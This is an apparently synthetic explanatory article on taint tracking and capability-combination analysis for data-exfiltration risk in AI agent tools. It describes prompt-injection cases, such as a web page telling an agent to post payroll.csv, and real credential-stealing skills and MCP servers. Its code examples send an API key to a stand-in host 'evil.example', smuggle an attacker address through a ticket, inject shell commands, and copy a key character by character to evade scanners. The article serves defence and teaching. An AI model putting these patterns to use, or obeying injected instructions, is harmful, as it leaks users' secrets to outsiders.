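# Single-function taint tracking and capability-combination analysis for data exfiltration risk in AI agents

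## Agents, tools and the two ways data can leak

Single-function taint tracking and capability-combination analysis are two methods for judging whether an AI agent could leak private data. An AI agent is a language model that calls tools in a loop to carry out a task. A tool is a function the model can call, such as one that reads a file or sends an email. Data can leak in two ways. The code of a single tool may send it out, or the model may read it with one tool and pass it to another. Taint tracking suits leaks in a tool's code because the analyst follows a value through that code line by line. For leaks through the model, the more suitable method is capability-combination analysis, in which the analyst lists what the agent can do and looks for dangerous combinations.

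### The agent loop

The software developer Simon Willison avoided the word "agent" for years because everyone seemed to mean something different by it. In *I think "agent" may finally have a widely enough agreed upon definition* (2025), he settled on defining an agent as a language model that "runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal".

Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a guide for developers building on its Claude models, describes the loop step by step. The application (the ordinary program around the model) sends the model the user's request and a list of tools. Each tool has a name, a plain-language description and a schema that formally specifies the arguments it accepts. The model cannot run anything itself, so it replies with a structured request that names a tool and fills in the arguments. The application runs the function, then sends the model the whole conversation again with the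 output added at the end. The model then returns either another request or its final answer. The text the model receives at each step is its context, which grows with every round.

The model receives a tool's schema and results but never its code, so it cannot detect when the tool does more than its description states. Each result also stays in the context, where the model can copy any part of it into the arguments of a later call. Agents need this ability for ordinary tasks, such as looking up a customer's address and putting it on a letter.

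### MCP servers and skills

Many of an agent's tools come from people its user doesn't know. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a standard that servers use to offer tools to agents. Anthropic introduced it in 2024 to connect AI applications with outside systems (Granados, 2026, *MCP 2026 changes the rules*). By July 2026, developers were downloading its main software kits nearly half a billion times a month, according to the project's own blog (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

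An MCP server is a program, on the user's machine or on the internet, that lists its tools and runs them on request. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), a chapter of the specification, gives the example of a tool named `get_weather`, with the description "Get current weather information for a location". It takes one argument, a city name or zip code. Calling it with "New York" returns a short text that gives the temperature as 72°F and the conditions as partly cloudy.

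One agent can use several servers at once. Under the design rules in Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), a server should not be able to read the whole conversation or look into other servers. The full history stays with the host, the application that runs the model. When an agent uses two servers, the host therefore holds data from both, and the model can read it. The rules govern what passes over the protocol and do not by themselves stop a server on the user's machine from opening files there.

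The July 2026 version of the protocol explicitly relies on the model to carry data between tool calls. It has no sessions, so a shop's server that needs to remember a basket returns an identifier such as `bsk_a1b2c3`, and the model passes it back when adding an item. The model can copy a password from a tool's output into a later call in the same way.

A skill is an installable folder of instructions that an agent loads when needed. It contains a file named SKILL.md and, optionally, scripts and reference documents. Anthropic introduced the format in October 2025, in *Equipping agents for the real world with Agent Skills*, and published it as an open standard that December. According to the standard's website, Agent Skills, an agent reads only each skill's name and description at startup. When a task matches a skill, the agent reads the full instructions, follows them, and may run the bundled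 scripts.

Gandhi, Aviv and colleagues (2026) point out in *Scan Before You Install* that those scripts can reach the file system, the shell and the network under whatever permissions the user has granted. Skills can be published with little vetting. According to *ASTELD* (2026), a paper proposing a classification of autonomous agents, the skill marketplace ClawHub required only that publishers have a GitHub account at least a week old.

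### Prompt injection and exfiltration

Prompt injection is text that someone plants in content the agent reads, hoping the model will follow it as an instruction. Willison named it after SQL injection, an older attack in which a visitor to a website types database commands into a form. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) explains that prompt injection works because the user's request, the web page and the tool outputs all end up in one sequence of tokens, and the model cannot reliably tell whose instructions to follow. If a user asks for a summary of a web page, and the page contains a sentence saying that the user wants some private data emailed to a stranger, there is a fair chance that the model will send the email.

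Programmers can stop SQL injection by separating commands from data, but Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) says a language model "inherently does not distinguish between the two". The agency prefers to think of the model as a confusable deputy, a privileged program that an outsider can trick into misusing its privileges for them. In December 2025 it warned that prompt injection "may never be totally mitigated", as quoted in Computer Weekly's *NCSC warns of confusion over true nature of AI prompt injection*.

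Newer models resist prompt injection much better. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) reports a public competition in which 464 people made 272,000 attempts against 13 leading models and succeeded 8,648 times, or about 3%. Success rates ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. For the later Claude Opus 5, The Decoder reported a success rate of 2.0% after 15 attempts in a test by the security firm Gray Swan, down from 5.5% for Opus 4.8. It also reported no successes in 129 browser scenarios. *INFUSE*, a benchmark from October 2026, found that an average of 19.6% of attacked runs ended in compromise, but it covers a wider pool of models, including small, older ones such as GPT-4o-mini, so the figures are not directly comparable.

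An attacker can also usually try more than once. If each attempt had an independent 0.5% chance of success, 200 emails would give roughly a 63% chance of at least one success. Real attempts are not independent, and a good defence may block a whole family of them. Still, it seems prudent to ask what an agent could do when an injection works.

The usual aim is exfiltration, which means sending private data to someone not entitled to it. Willison calls the channels "almost limitless". They include a request to a web service, an image that loads from the attacker's site, and a link that the user clicks. Some channels hardly look like communication, such as DNS, the system that turns a domain name into a network address. An attacker who runs the server for a domain can read any text that someone puts in the name. *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* (Poireault,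 September 2026) reported on weaknesses in Salesforce's agents that exposed customer records through prompt injection and DNS.

### A leak in a tool's code

Santra, Kirat and colleagues (2026), in *ACaM*, open with a weather tool. Its description promises a forecast for a city, and the forecast arrives. The same function also reads a credentials file and sends the contents out in the header of a web request. Every ordinary question about the weather leaks the credentials again. Nobody has to trick the model, which calls the tool for its stated purpose and gets what it expected. (Earlier studies that Santra and colleagues cite found a mismatch between description and code in 10% to 13% of cases.)

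A skill named weather-data-fetcher stole data in much the same way. Gen Agent Trust Hub's audit *weather-data-fetcher* (February 2026) traces the theft to a file named index.js. One function in that file reads `~/.clawdbot/.env`, a type of settings file that usually holds API keys (the passwords that programs use with online services), and another posts the contents to an address on webhook.site. Because the read and the send are in separate functions, an analysis that looks at one function at a time could easily miss the link between them.

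Socket's *weather-data-fetcher* (2026), an audit from the same afternoon, reached the same finding with 90% confidence but allowed that the script might be test code. The code shows where the keys go, but the author's motive can only be guessed. Socket also noticed that the script prints the file's contents as ordinary output. An agent that runs a script normally reads its output, so the keys would probably also enter the model's context.

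Private data can come from a tool's arguments as well as from files. The package postmark-mcp was an MCP server for sending email, copied from the genuine server made by the email company Postmark. According to Koi Security, the firm that found the leak, its first fifteen versions worked properly. Version 1.0.16, which The Hacker News (2025) dates to 17 September 2025, added a single line that sent a blind copy of every email to the package's author. The user's agent had passed the private text to the tool as an argument, which the tool needed to send the email.

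### A leak through the model

Now suppose an agent has three tools that work as described. `fetch_page` downloads a web page, `read_file` returns the contents of a file, and `post_to_web` sends text to an address. The user asks for a summary of a page that contains instructions in small print to open payroll.csv and submit its contents to a web form "to complete the summary". If the model follows these instructions, it calls `read_file`, which adds the payroll to its context, and then passes the payroll to `post_to_web`.

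A reviewer could study all three functions carefully and find nothing wrong. `read_file` returns a string to its caller, `post_to_web` sends whatever string it receives, and no code connects the two. The model connected them during one run because of what it had just read.

A secret can leak without the model handling it. Gandhi and colleagues describe a backup skill that copies the user's private keys and cloud credentials into an archive in a shared folder. A debugging skill by a different author treats recent files in that folder as diagnostic logs and uploads them to a public clipboard service. An attacker who controls a page that the agent reads only has to get the model to run the two skills in that order, because the credentials pass between them on disk.

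### What each method can answer

Taint tracking and capability-combination analysis are both mainly forms of static analysis, which examines a program without running it. Runtime analysis monitors the agent as it runs and can stop a call before any data leaves, but it covers only the calls the agent actually makes. Static analysis can cover code that no test run reached, before anyone installs the tool. Santra and colleagues argue that defenders have put most of their effort into runtime analysis, although a leak like the weather tool's is visible in the code before the tool runs.

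As a runtime check, the MCP specification recommends showing the user each tool's inputs before the call is made. This would help with the payroll, because the user would see it before it went to a stranger's web form. It wouldn't help with the weather tool, because the user would see only `get_weather` and "New York". For tools that run on the model provider's own servers, such as Anthropic's web search, the developer usually sees the call only after it has finished.

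Taint tracking begins with a list of sources and a list of sinks. A source is a place where secret or untrusted data enters the code, such as the line that opens a credentials file. A sink is an operation where such data can do harm, such as an outbound request or a shell command. The software labels the value at the source as tainted and follows it from variable to variable to see whether it can reach a sink. In the weather tool it can, and the software reports the path so that a person can check it. The path does not prove theft, though. The clean versions of postmark-mcp also had to send the text of emails over the network, and the malicious line only changed who received a copy.

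Taint tracking finds no flow for the payroll data, because the label leaves `read_file` at the return statement and nothing in the code carries it further. Extending the trace through the model is difficult. Santra and colleagues observe that analysers for ordinary software assume the code fixes which parts can reach which, whereas a model chooses its calls at runtime and may choose differently next time. An analyst could assume that the model passes labels from everything it reads to everything it writes, but then every agent with a file reader and a web poster would show a flow, including harmless ones. Santra and colleagues add that this approximation also misses real problems.

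Capability-combination analysis checks whether an agent has every capability an attacker would need to steal data, without tracing a path the data could take. A capability is a kind of action that a tool or skill makes possible, such as reading files or sending network requests. The dangerous combination is access to private data, a way for an attacker to put instructions in front of the model, and a way to send the data out (Willison's "lethal trifecta"). The payroll agent has all three. So does nearly any assistant that reads and sends email, because strangers can write to it, though most of those assistants may never leak anything. The method can also miss real leaks, since an analyst who works from tool descriptions would classify `get_weather` as a harmless lookup.

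### Precision and recall

Two numbers describe how often a scanner errs in each direction. Precision is the share of its flags that are right. Recall is the share of the real problems that it flags. With TP for correct flags, FP for false alarms and FN for problems missed:

precision = TP / (TP + FP)

recall = TP / (TP + FN)

Gandhi and colleagues ran a scanner over 1,587 public skills and got 59 findings about individual skills. Three analysts confirmed 53 of them, a precision of 89.8%. This scan can't measure recall, which requires a test set with known answers, because nobody knows how many flaws the scanner missed. On one such test set, with 267 risky groups of skills, the rule-based part of the scanner found 146 (54.7% recall) and raised no false alarms (100% precision).

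Precision also depends on what share of the scanned tools leak, so a scanner's precision on a test set may not hold in a marketplace. For example, a scanner that catches 95% of leaking tools and wrongly flags 5% of harmless ones has a precision of 95% on a test set where half the tools leak. In a marketplace of 10,000 tools where 100 leak, the same scanner finds 95 of them and raises 495 false alarms, so its precision is only 16%.

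## Tracing labels through one tool function, line by line

The Python function below is short enough for an analyst to track taint by hand. A company's support agent calls it to forward the next customer ticket to a help desk at `desk.example.com`, which accepts only messages that contain the company's API key.

```python
def forward_ticket():
    ticket = fetch_next_ticket()                    # line 1
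    key = os.environ["DESK_API_KEY"]                # line 2
    host = "desk.example.com"                       # line 3
    if "urgent" in ticket:                          # line 4
        host = ticket.split()[-1]                   # line 5
    payload = {"ticket": ticket, "key": key}        # line 6
    requests.post("https://" + host, json=payload)  # line 7
```

The flaw is in lines 4 and 5, which take the last word of an urgent ticket as the address. Perhaps a programmer added them so that an urgent ticket could name a different desk, but anyone can write a ticket. A stranger who writes "This is urgent, please use evil.example" receives the company's key. The stranger doesn't have to trick the model, because the function itself reads the ticket and acts on it.

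### Two labels for every value

Every value gets an integrity label and a confidentiality label. The integrity label is "untrusted" if an outsider could have chosen the value, and "trusted" if not. The confidentiality label is "secret" if outsiders must not see the value, and "public" if they may. The ticket is untrusted because a stranger wrote it, and public because in this example it contains nothing private. The key is trusted and secret. The address on line 3 is trusted and public, like any constant the programmer typed.

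For the arithmetic, let 0 stand for trusted or public and 1 for untrusted or secret, with integrity first. The ticket's label is then (1, 0), the key's is (0, 1) and a constant's is (0, 0). When code combines two values, the result takes the larger number in each position. Computer scientists call this operation the join and write it ⊔:

(i₁, c₁) ⊔ (i₂, c₂) = (max(i₁, i₂), max(c₁, c₂))

Joining the ticket with the key gives (1, 1), the label of a value that an outsider partly chose and that contains a secret.

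The assignment rule follows directly. If a line computes y from x₁ to xₙ, the new label of y is

L(y) := L(x₁) ⊔ L(x₂) ⊔ … ⊔ L(xₙ)

Assigning to y replaces both its value and its label. At an `if`, the algorithm analyzes both branches, because either one might run. Where the branches meet, each variable takes the join of its labels from the ends of the two branches. The algorithm analyzes a loop's body repeatedly until a pass changes no labels.

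The assignment rule applies even when y is only derived from x. GitHub's *About data flow analysis*, a guide to the company's code-analysis engine CodeQL, explains that ordinary data flow analysis follows a value only while it stays the same, so it stops at `y = x + 1`, while taint tracking continues to y. Tracing the label through line 5 requires taint tracking because the new host is only a fragment of the ticket.

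### The trace

The table shows both labels of every variable after each line. A dash means that the variable doesn't exist yet.

| After | `ticket` | `key` | `host` | `payload` |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| line 1 | untrusted, public | – | – | – |
| line 2 | untrusted, public | trusted, secret | – | – |
| line 3 | untrusted, public | trusted, secret | trusted, public | – |
| line 4 | untrusted, public | trusted, secret | trusted, public | – |
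| line 5 (if it runs) | untrusted, public | trusted, secret | untrusted, public | – |
| the branches meet | untrusted, public | trusted, secret | untrusted, public | – |
| line 6 | untrusted, public | trusted, secret | untrusted, public | untrusted, secret |
| line 7 | untrusted, public | trusted, secret | untrusted, public | untrusted, secret |

The host has the label (0, 0) if the code skips line 5 and (1, 0) if it doesn't, and the join of the two is (1, 0). The request on line 7 is the sink. The analyser reports the path because the request sends a secret payload to an address that an outsider could have chosen.

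The analyst has to decide which labels to flag at the sink. A rule that flags every secret payload would flag this function even without lines 4 and 5, when it sends the key only to the desk that needs it. A rule that flags every untrusted host would flag any tool that opens a link from a user. A narrower rule flags the request only if the host is untrusted and the payload is secret. *Advanced taint analysis techniques*, part of the manual for the widely used code scanner Semgrep, describes an experimental feature that fits this case. It lets users label each kind of source and require a different label for each argument of the sink.

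This narrower rule would miss the malicious weather tool. Its author hard-coded the destination, so an analyser would label that destination trusted. The integrity label protects a programmer from outsiders, so it doesn't help when the programmer is the attacker. For a tool written by a stranger, the analyst has to flag every secret that leaves and check by hand where each one goes, even though many of the flagged cases will be legitimate logins.

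The trace also gives the whole payload one label, although only one of its two fields is secret. If a later line sent just `payload["ticket"]` to an untrusted host, the analyser would raise a false alarm. Analysers can avoid this by labelling fields separately, which Semgrep supports to a limited degree.

### Why the two labels need separate scales

These rules date back to 1976, when Dorothy Denning examined how a computer could stop information from moving, even indirectly, from a secret file into a less secret one. In *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, she sorted information into classes and wrote A → B if information in class A may flow into class B.

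Denning then worked out what any consistent set of such permissions must look like. If a program may run `b := a` and then `c := b`, forbidding `c := a` makes no sense, so permissions have to carry over from step to step. Each operand must also be allowed to flow into the class of the result. Otherwise a program could be barred from `c := a` but free to run `c := a + b`, which does the same thing when b is 0. With a finite number of classes and a lowest class for harmless data, these requirements produce a lattice. In a lattice, any two classes have a least upper bound, or join, which is the lowest class into which both may flow.

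Because permitted flows are transitive, a sequence of statements is allowed if each statement is, so an analyser can check a program one statement at a time. *Lattice-Based Access Control Models* (Sandhu, 1993), a tutorial on computer security, still began with Denning's axioms as the theoretical foundation of the field.

The simplest lattice is a single scale, such as public, internal and secret. Santra and colleagues explain that this doesn't work for agents because untrusted data is usually public, which puts it at the bottom of the scale, and a join with anything higher erases its origin. The two possible hosts in `forward_ticket` would both be public, so the analyser could not distinguish the company's own desk from an address in a stranger's ticket.

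Moving untrusted data to the top of the scale would not help, because the join of two labels on any single scale is the higher of the two. The payload would have the same label as either the ticket or the key, and the analyser would lose a fact it needs. Two scales give four labels, and (1, 1) lies above both (1, 0) and (0, 1). Denning described such a combination in ADEPT-50, a time-sharing system that paired a military secrecy level with a set of project categories. Santra and colleagues likewise track exfiltration and injection in parallel.

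### Loops, and why the algorithm stops

One pass through a loop can be too few. This fragment keeps the three most recent tickets:

```python
first = second = third = ""
for _ in range(10):
    third = second
    second = first
    first = fetch_next_ticket()
```

All three variables start as trusted and public. The confidentiality labels never change, so the table shows integrity only.

| After pass | `first` | `second` | `third` |
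|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | untrusted | trusted | trusted |
| 2 | untrusted | untrusted | trusted |
| 3 | untrusted | untrusted | untrusted |
| 4 | untrusted | untrusted | untrusted |

On the first pass, the algorithm copies `second` and `first` while they are still clean, then reads a ticket. The taint moves one variable per pass and reaches `third` on pass 3. Pass 4 changes nothing, so the algorithm stops. An analyser that stopped after one pass would wrongly mark `third` as safe to use as a host.

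The algorithm always stops because it can raise only a limited number of labels. A function with n variables has 2n labels, each either 0 or 1. A line inside the loop may lower a label temporarily, for example by assigning a constant. But each time the algorithm returns to the top of the loop, it joins the new labels with those from earlier passes, so labels at that point never fall and each can rise only once. Every pass except the last must raise at least one label, so there are at most 2n such passes, plus a final one that confirms nothing has changed. The fragment has three variables, and the algorithm raises three of a possible six labels. The limit doesn't depend on how many times the real loop runs.

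In *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* (Denning and Denning, 1977), the programmer declares a fixed class for every variable, and the compiler checks each assignment against the declarations as it reads the program, without repetition. A programmer would declare `host` as trusted, and the compiler would reject line 5 immediately. Ordinary Python code contains no such declarations, so a scanner has to infer the labels.

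### Why no analyser can be exact

Denning and Denning showed that no analyser can flag exactly the functions that can leak. Suppose a function runs an arbitrary program and then posts the key to a stranger. The key leaks only if the program finishes, so an exact analyser would have to determine whether any given program finishes. This is the halting problem, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm solves it.

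Denning and Denning therefore settled for a stricter test that a compiler can carry out. It rejects a program if the text contains a forbidden flow, whether or not that flow could ever happen. A Python version of their example is

```python
if debug:
    if not debug:
        requests.post("https://evil.example", data=key)
```

The post can never run, because `debug` can't be both true and false, but the test still rejects the code. By accepting such false alarms, they were able to prove that their compiler certifies a program only if it is secure with respect to the kinds of flow their model covers.

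Commercial scanners generally don't offer that guarantee. Semgrep's *Dataflow analysis engine overview* tells users to expect both false positives and false negatives. The scanner produces false positives because it considers every path through the code, including impossible ones like the path above. It can also miss real leaks because it ignores how `eval`-like functions, which run text as code, change the program's state.

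Another source of misses is aliasing, where two names refer to the same object. Suppose `forward_ticket` put only the ticket in `payload` and then ran these lines:

```python
box = payload
box["key"] = key
```

The payload now contains the key, because `box` and `payload` are the same dictionary. Semgrep tracks taint by variable, not by object in memory, so it would label `box` and leave `payload` clean. The flow stays inside the function, so the limits of single-function analysis don't explain the miss.

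### An allow-list for the host

The obvious repair is to check the address just before line 7:

```python
if host not in {"desk.example.com", "urgent.example.com"}:
    raise ValueError("unknown host")
```

After this check, a stranger can at most choose between two of the company's own desks. The check is a sanitiser for the host. It changes the host's integrity label from untrusted to trusted, so the narrow rule no longer flags line 7. The key is still secret, so a rule against every secret payload would still flag the request. The ticket text is still untrusted and would be just as dangerous in a shell command as it was before the check.

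Single-function analysis can handle this version if it recognises the check. Otherwise, the host keeps its untrusted label and the analyser flags the repaired function. The analyst can prevent this by declaring the check. A Semgrep rule can name a function such as `check_if_safe(x)` and treat x as clean after the call. Since April 2026, CodeQL users can declare their project's own sanitisers and validators without writing custom CodeQL, according to GitHub's *CodeQL now supports sanitizers and validators in models-as-data* (2026).

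The analyser does not verify these declarations. If the programmer had written `host.endswith("example.com")`, the check would accept `evil-example.com`, which anyone could register. If an analyst declared this check a sanitiser, the analyser would miss a leak it would otherwise have flagged. A careless declaration can also cover too much code. Semgrep warns about an old workaround that treated every use of a variable after the check as clean, even if the program had since assigned new untrusted data to it.

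### A helper whose code is missing

Suppose line 5 reads `host = pick_desk(ticket)`, and `pick_desk` comes from a library whose source the analyser doesn't have. The helper might look up the ticket's topic in a table and return one of the company's addresses, or it might return a word from the ticket, and the analyser has to guess which.

By default, Semgrep assumes that a function it can't examine passes taint from any argument to its result. It therefore treats the host as untrusted and flags line 7, which is a false alarm if the helper takes the host from a fixed table. With the option `taint_assume_safe_functions`, Semgrep assumes the opposite and misses the leak if the helper copies the host from the ticket. In the free Community Edition, Semgrep has to make one of these assumptions for every call, even when the helper is defined in the same file.

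The default assumption resembles a 1977 rule from Denning and Denning, who treated calls to functions such as SORT and LOG like ordinary expressions, whose class is the join of the arguments' classes. They allowed this only if the procedure computed its result entirely from its arguments and public data, and wrote to nothing else outside itself. Library code often breaks those conditions. For example, a helper called `auth_header()` could take no arguments, read the key from a file and return it. Since the helper has no tainted arguments, the default assumption treats its result as untainted, and the analyser misses the secret unless someone has listed the helper as a source.

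A call can also change one of its arguments. In an example from Semgrep, a program adds user input to a set with `s.add(x)` and later takes an element out with `s.pop()`. The scanner misses this flow until a rule's author writes a propagator, which marks `s` as tainted when `x` is tainted.

A function summary replaces guesswork with a short statement of which inputs can affect which outputs or sinks. LLVM's *Taint Analysis Configuration* has one for the C function `dirname`, which returns the folder part of a file path. According to that summary, the result is tainted if the path is. GitHub's *Customizing Library Models for Python* describes a format in which CodeQL users can write summaries of library functions by hand. A summary of `pick_desk` would settle whether the ticket can affect the address, as long as whoever wrote it had read the helper's code correctly.

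### A post in another function

A programmer might tidy up the code by moving the request into a function of its own:

```python
def send(host, payload):
    requests.post("https://" + host, json=payload)
```

Line 7 of `forward_ticket` becomes `send(host, payload)`. The program behaves as before and still leaks the key, but single-function analysis now misses the leak. The analyser computes the right labels for `host` and `payload` in `forward_ticket`, but the sink is now in `send`, where those labels depend on the caller. The analyst could configure it to treat all parameters as both untrusted and secret, but then it would flag `send` in every program, including those that only send a constant to a fixed address.

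Cross-function analysis solves this by examining the code of `send` once and recording in a summary that the first argument reaches the address of a request and the second reaches the body. It then applies the summary at the call in `forward_ticket`, where the labels are known, and reports the leak.

Denning and Denning described an early form of this. For each procedure, the compiler listed the classes that its inputs and outputs required. For each call, it listed the classes of the values that the caller supplied. The linker, which joins separately compiled parts, then compared the lists. With fixed classes, though, a library procedure that had to accept secrets needed inputs and outputs in the highest class, so its results counted as secret even when a caller gave it only public data. Denning and Denning considered compiling a separate version for every combination of input classes, but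 doubted that this was workable when there were many. For procedures that met the conditions above, a better solution was to check the outputs at each call against the arguments actually supplied. Modern summaries also relate outputs to inputs this way.

Scanners now differ in how far they follow data, partly for commercial reasons. Semgrep limits its free Community Edition to single-function analysis to keep it fast and simple to set up. The paid product, Semgrep Code, follows data between functions in the same file by default and between files as an option. It falls back to analysing one file at a time if preparing a cross-file scan takes more than 5 GB of memory or the scan lasts more than three hours. Most agent tools are probably much too small to reach those limits.

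CodeQL offers both kinds of analysis and calls them local and global data flow. Local flow tracks values within one function, and global flow also follows them through calls and object properties. GitHub's *Analyzing data flow in Python* describes local flow as faster, more precise and often sufficient. For a global search, the analyst writes one test to identify sources and another to identify sinks. One of the guide's examples tracks environment variables, the kind of source on line 2, to the places where a program opens files. An analyst could look for the leak in `send` by replacing the file-opening sink with outbound requests and adding taint steps.

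*AGENT AUDIT* (Zhang, Nian and Zhao, 2026) describes a scanner that tracks taint only within single functions, even though it was designed for agent code. This limit matters for real thefts such as the one by the weather-data-fetcher skill, which used two functions. Both were in the same file, so an analysis that crosses functions but not files should in principle be enough to connect them.

### A branch that leaks without copying

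Everything so far has followed data as the program copies or combines it. A program can also reveal a secret without copying any of it:

```python
flag = "0"
if key.startswith("a"):
    flag = "1"
requests.post("https://" + host, data=flag)
```

The variable `flag` receives only constants, so under the assignment rule it stays trusted and public. Yet whoever receives the request learns whether the key begins with "a". Denning and Denning call this an implicit flow, as opposed to the explicit flow of an assignment. In their example, y starts at 1, and the program sets it to 0 if x is 0. If x can only be 0 or 1, y ends up equal to x.

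An attacker needn't stop at one bit. The next fragment rebuilds the whole key:

```python
copy = ""
for ch in key:
    for letter in ALPHABET:
        if ch == letter:
            copy += letter
```

Every letter in `copy` comes from the constant `ALPHABET`, so an analyser that follows only explicit flows would label the finished copy public.

The remedy is to include the condition in the join. Inside a branch, every assignment also takes on the label of the condition that controls it:

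L(y) := L(x₁) ⊔ … ⊔ L(xₙ) ⊔ L(condition)

With this rule, `flag` becomes secret inside the branch and stays secret where the branches meet. The analyser can then report the post, even though the whole leak is inside one function.

Static analysis has an advantage here because it examines both branches. Denning illustrates this with a program by J. S. Fenton, in which a is a secret that is either true or false:

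```python
b = c = False
if not a:
    c = True
if not c:
    b = True
```

A monitor that updates labels only when an assignment runs would miss the leak, even if it used the rule for conditions. If a is true, the program skips the first assignment, so c stays false and public. The test on c then succeeds, and b becomes true with a public label. If a is false, c becomes true and secret, but the program skips the second assignment, so b stays false and public. In both cases b equals a but is labelled public. A static analyser examines the first branch whether or not it would run, so it labels c secret and then b secret too.

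Common scanners don't apply the rule by default. CodeQL's data flow graph has no node for an `if` statement because, as GitHub explains, the statement doesn't carry a value. Semgrep doesn't report `sink("foo" if tainted else "bar")`, an example from its *Taint analysis overview*, because neither "foo" nor "bar" is tainted. Rule writers can change a setting so that Semgrep reports any tainted expression inside the sink's brackets, but that wouldn't catch `flag`, because the test on the key is in an earlier statement. Semgrep also has an option for tracking control, but it only checks whether one piece of code can run after another.

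There is a reasonable case for leaving implicit flows out, because tracking them can flag harmless functions. Suppose line 5 of `forward_ticket` were `host = "urgent.example.com"`, another of the company's desks. A stranger could then choose between two safe addresses by writing or omitting the word "urgent". The rule for conditions would label the host untrusted, and the analyser would flag the function. Programs constantly branch on outside input, so false alarms could outnumber leaks. Leaving implicit flows out is riskier when a tool's author may be hostile, since anyone who knows how the scanner works can write the `ALPHABET` loop to evade it.

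The rule for conditions still misses some leaks. Denning and Denning describe a loop that keeps adding a secret number to a total and publishes a counter each time, until the total gets too large and the program crashes. The last published count reveals the approximate size of the secret, although the secret doesn't appear in any `if` or loop condition. They proposed a way to handle such crashes, but left out what they call covert channels, such as running time and power consumption. A tool could leak information about the key this way by waiting a number of seconds that depends on the key and then sending an empty request.

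### A secret returned to the model

Finally, suppose that `forward_ticket` has a safe, fixed host, and that a programmer adds a last line to help with debugging:

```python
return "Sent: " + str(payload)
```

The returned text includes the ticket and the key, so it is labeled both untrusted and secret. Single-function analysis with the usual sinks (outbound requests, shell commands and so on) misses the exposed key, because the return statement isn't one of them. Cross-function analysis doesn't help either, because the text goes to the model, as the payroll did in the earlier example.

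Semgrep can treat any code its patterns match as a sink, so an analyst can add one for return statements in tool functions. But the analyser would then always flag a tool such as `read_file`, which exists to return private data. Santra and colleagues instead record whether a tool returns a secret as one property, and whether it sends a secret to an outside address as another.

The integrity label also matters, because the ticket could contain a prompt injection. With the debugging line, `forward_ticket` alone supplies two parts of the lethal trifecta, private data and untrusted content. An attacker then needs only a tool that can send text to an outside address, and an analyser limited to `forward_ticket` can't detect whether the agent has one.

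## Two scanners that look for taint in tool code: Agent Audit and VIPER-MCP

Agent Audit and VIPER-MCP apply taint tracking to the code of agent tools. Agent Audit, from March 2026, tracks data only within single functions and usually takes about a second. VIPER-MCP, from May 2026, follows data across functions and then has an agent test each suspected flaw, which takes about 15 minutes per server. Both look mainly for tools that an outsider can misuse, such as one that runs a stranger's text as a command. Neither is designed to follow a secret out of the program, so they cover only part of the exfiltration problem.

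### Agent Audit's four stages

Agent Audit mainly analyses Python. Suppose a programmer gives an agent this tool, which counts the lines in a file:

```python
@tool
def count_lines(path: str):
    command = "wc -l " + path
    return subprocess.run(command, shell=True, capture_output=True)
```

The `@tool` marker makes the function available to the model. The flaw is that `path` becomes part of a shell command, so whoever chooses the path can add a command of their own.

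Zhang and colleagues describe four stages. In the first, the scanner marks every function parameter as a source. It also marks the results of `chain.invoke()`, which returns a model's output, and `request.json()`, which returns data from a web request. Here it marks `path`.

In the second stage, the scanner builds a graph of which values feed into which others. The graph for `count_lines` has a link from `path` to `command` and another from `command` to the call that runs it.

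The third stage looks for sanitisers. The scanner recognises `shlex.quote()`, which makes the shell treat a string as a single argument, and parameterised queries, which keep data separate from database commands. It also accepts `isinstance()`, which checks a value's type.

In the fourth stage, the scanner searches the graph outward from each source, one link at a time, to check whether it can reach a sink. The sinks Zhang and colleagues name are `eval()`, which runs text as Python code, `subprocess.run()`, which starts another program, and `cursor.execute()`, which sends a command to a database. In `count_lines`, the search reaches `subprocess.run()` in two steps.

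### How one type check hides a finding

The scanner gives each finding a confidence score, which starts at 0.90 inside a tool function, where the arguments come from a model, and at 0.55 in any other function. If it finds a sanitiser, it multiplies the score by 0.20. It then sorts findings into four tiers: BLOCK (0.92 and above), WARN (0.60 and above), INFO (0.30 and above) and SUPPRESSED (below 0.30).

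| Location of the flaw | No sanitiser | With a sanitiser |
|---|---|---|
| Tool function | 0.90, WARN | 0.18, SUPPRESSED |
| Other function | 0.55, INFO | 0.11, SUPPRESSED |

These are starting points, because more than 20 other mechanisms can change a score, including a check for whether the code belongs to a test. A finding in a tool starts just below BLOCK, the top tier, so something else has to raise its score to get it there. Zhang and colleagues set the thresholds by experiment, so a score of 0.90 does not mean a 90% chance that the flaw is real.

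If the programmer changes the command to `"wc -l " + shlex.quote(path)`, nobody can add a second command through the path. The score falls to 0.90 × 0.20 = 0.18, and the scanner rightly suppresses the finding. But suppose the programmer leaves the command alone and adds a type check above it:

```python
if not isinstance(path, str):
    raise TypeError("path must be text")
```

A hostile path is also text, so it passes. The tool is as dangerous as before, but the score again falls to 0.18. The developer never sees the finding unless another rule or adjustment restores it.

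Type checks can be good sanitisers. If a tool needs a number, `isinstance(n, int)` keeps commands out, because an integer can't contain one. Whether the check helps depends on the type it tests for, but the flat multiplier is the same for every type. As with the allow-list for `host`, it also depends on the sink. For example, `shlex.quote()` returns `evil.example` unchanged, so it wouldn't protect the address of a web request.

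The multiplier is enough on its own to hide every finding in which the scanner recognises a sanitiser, because it would reduce even a perfect score of 1.00 to 0.20. A multiplier of 0.50 would have left the unsafe version of `count_lines` at 0.45, in the INFO tier, where a person could still look at it. It would also cause more false alarms about tools that use `shlex.quote()` correctly.

The single-function limit matters less here than in the earlier `send` example. Suppose the programmer moves the last line of `count_lines` into a helper called `run(command)`. Agent Audit can no longer trace the data back to `path`, but it treats `command` as a source because it is now a parameter of the helper. The scanner flags the helper with a score of 0.55. It would give the same score to a helper that only ever receives fixed commands, because it doesn't analyze the calls to the helper. A developer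 who reads only warnings and above would see neither finding.

### What the benchmark measured

Zhang and colleagues built a benchmark of 22 code samples containing 42 vulnerabilities that experts had marked in advance. Some samples reproduce vulnerabilities listed in CVE, the public catalogue of known software vulnerabilities. Others use patterns from real agent code, such as a calculator tool that passes its input to `eval()`. The benchmark also includes unsafe configuration files for MCP servers.

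Zhang and colleagues compared Agent Audit with Semgrep and with Bandit, a free Python checker that looks for risky patterns in code. The table gives the number of vulnerabilities each tool found, calculated from the paper's recall figures for each group.

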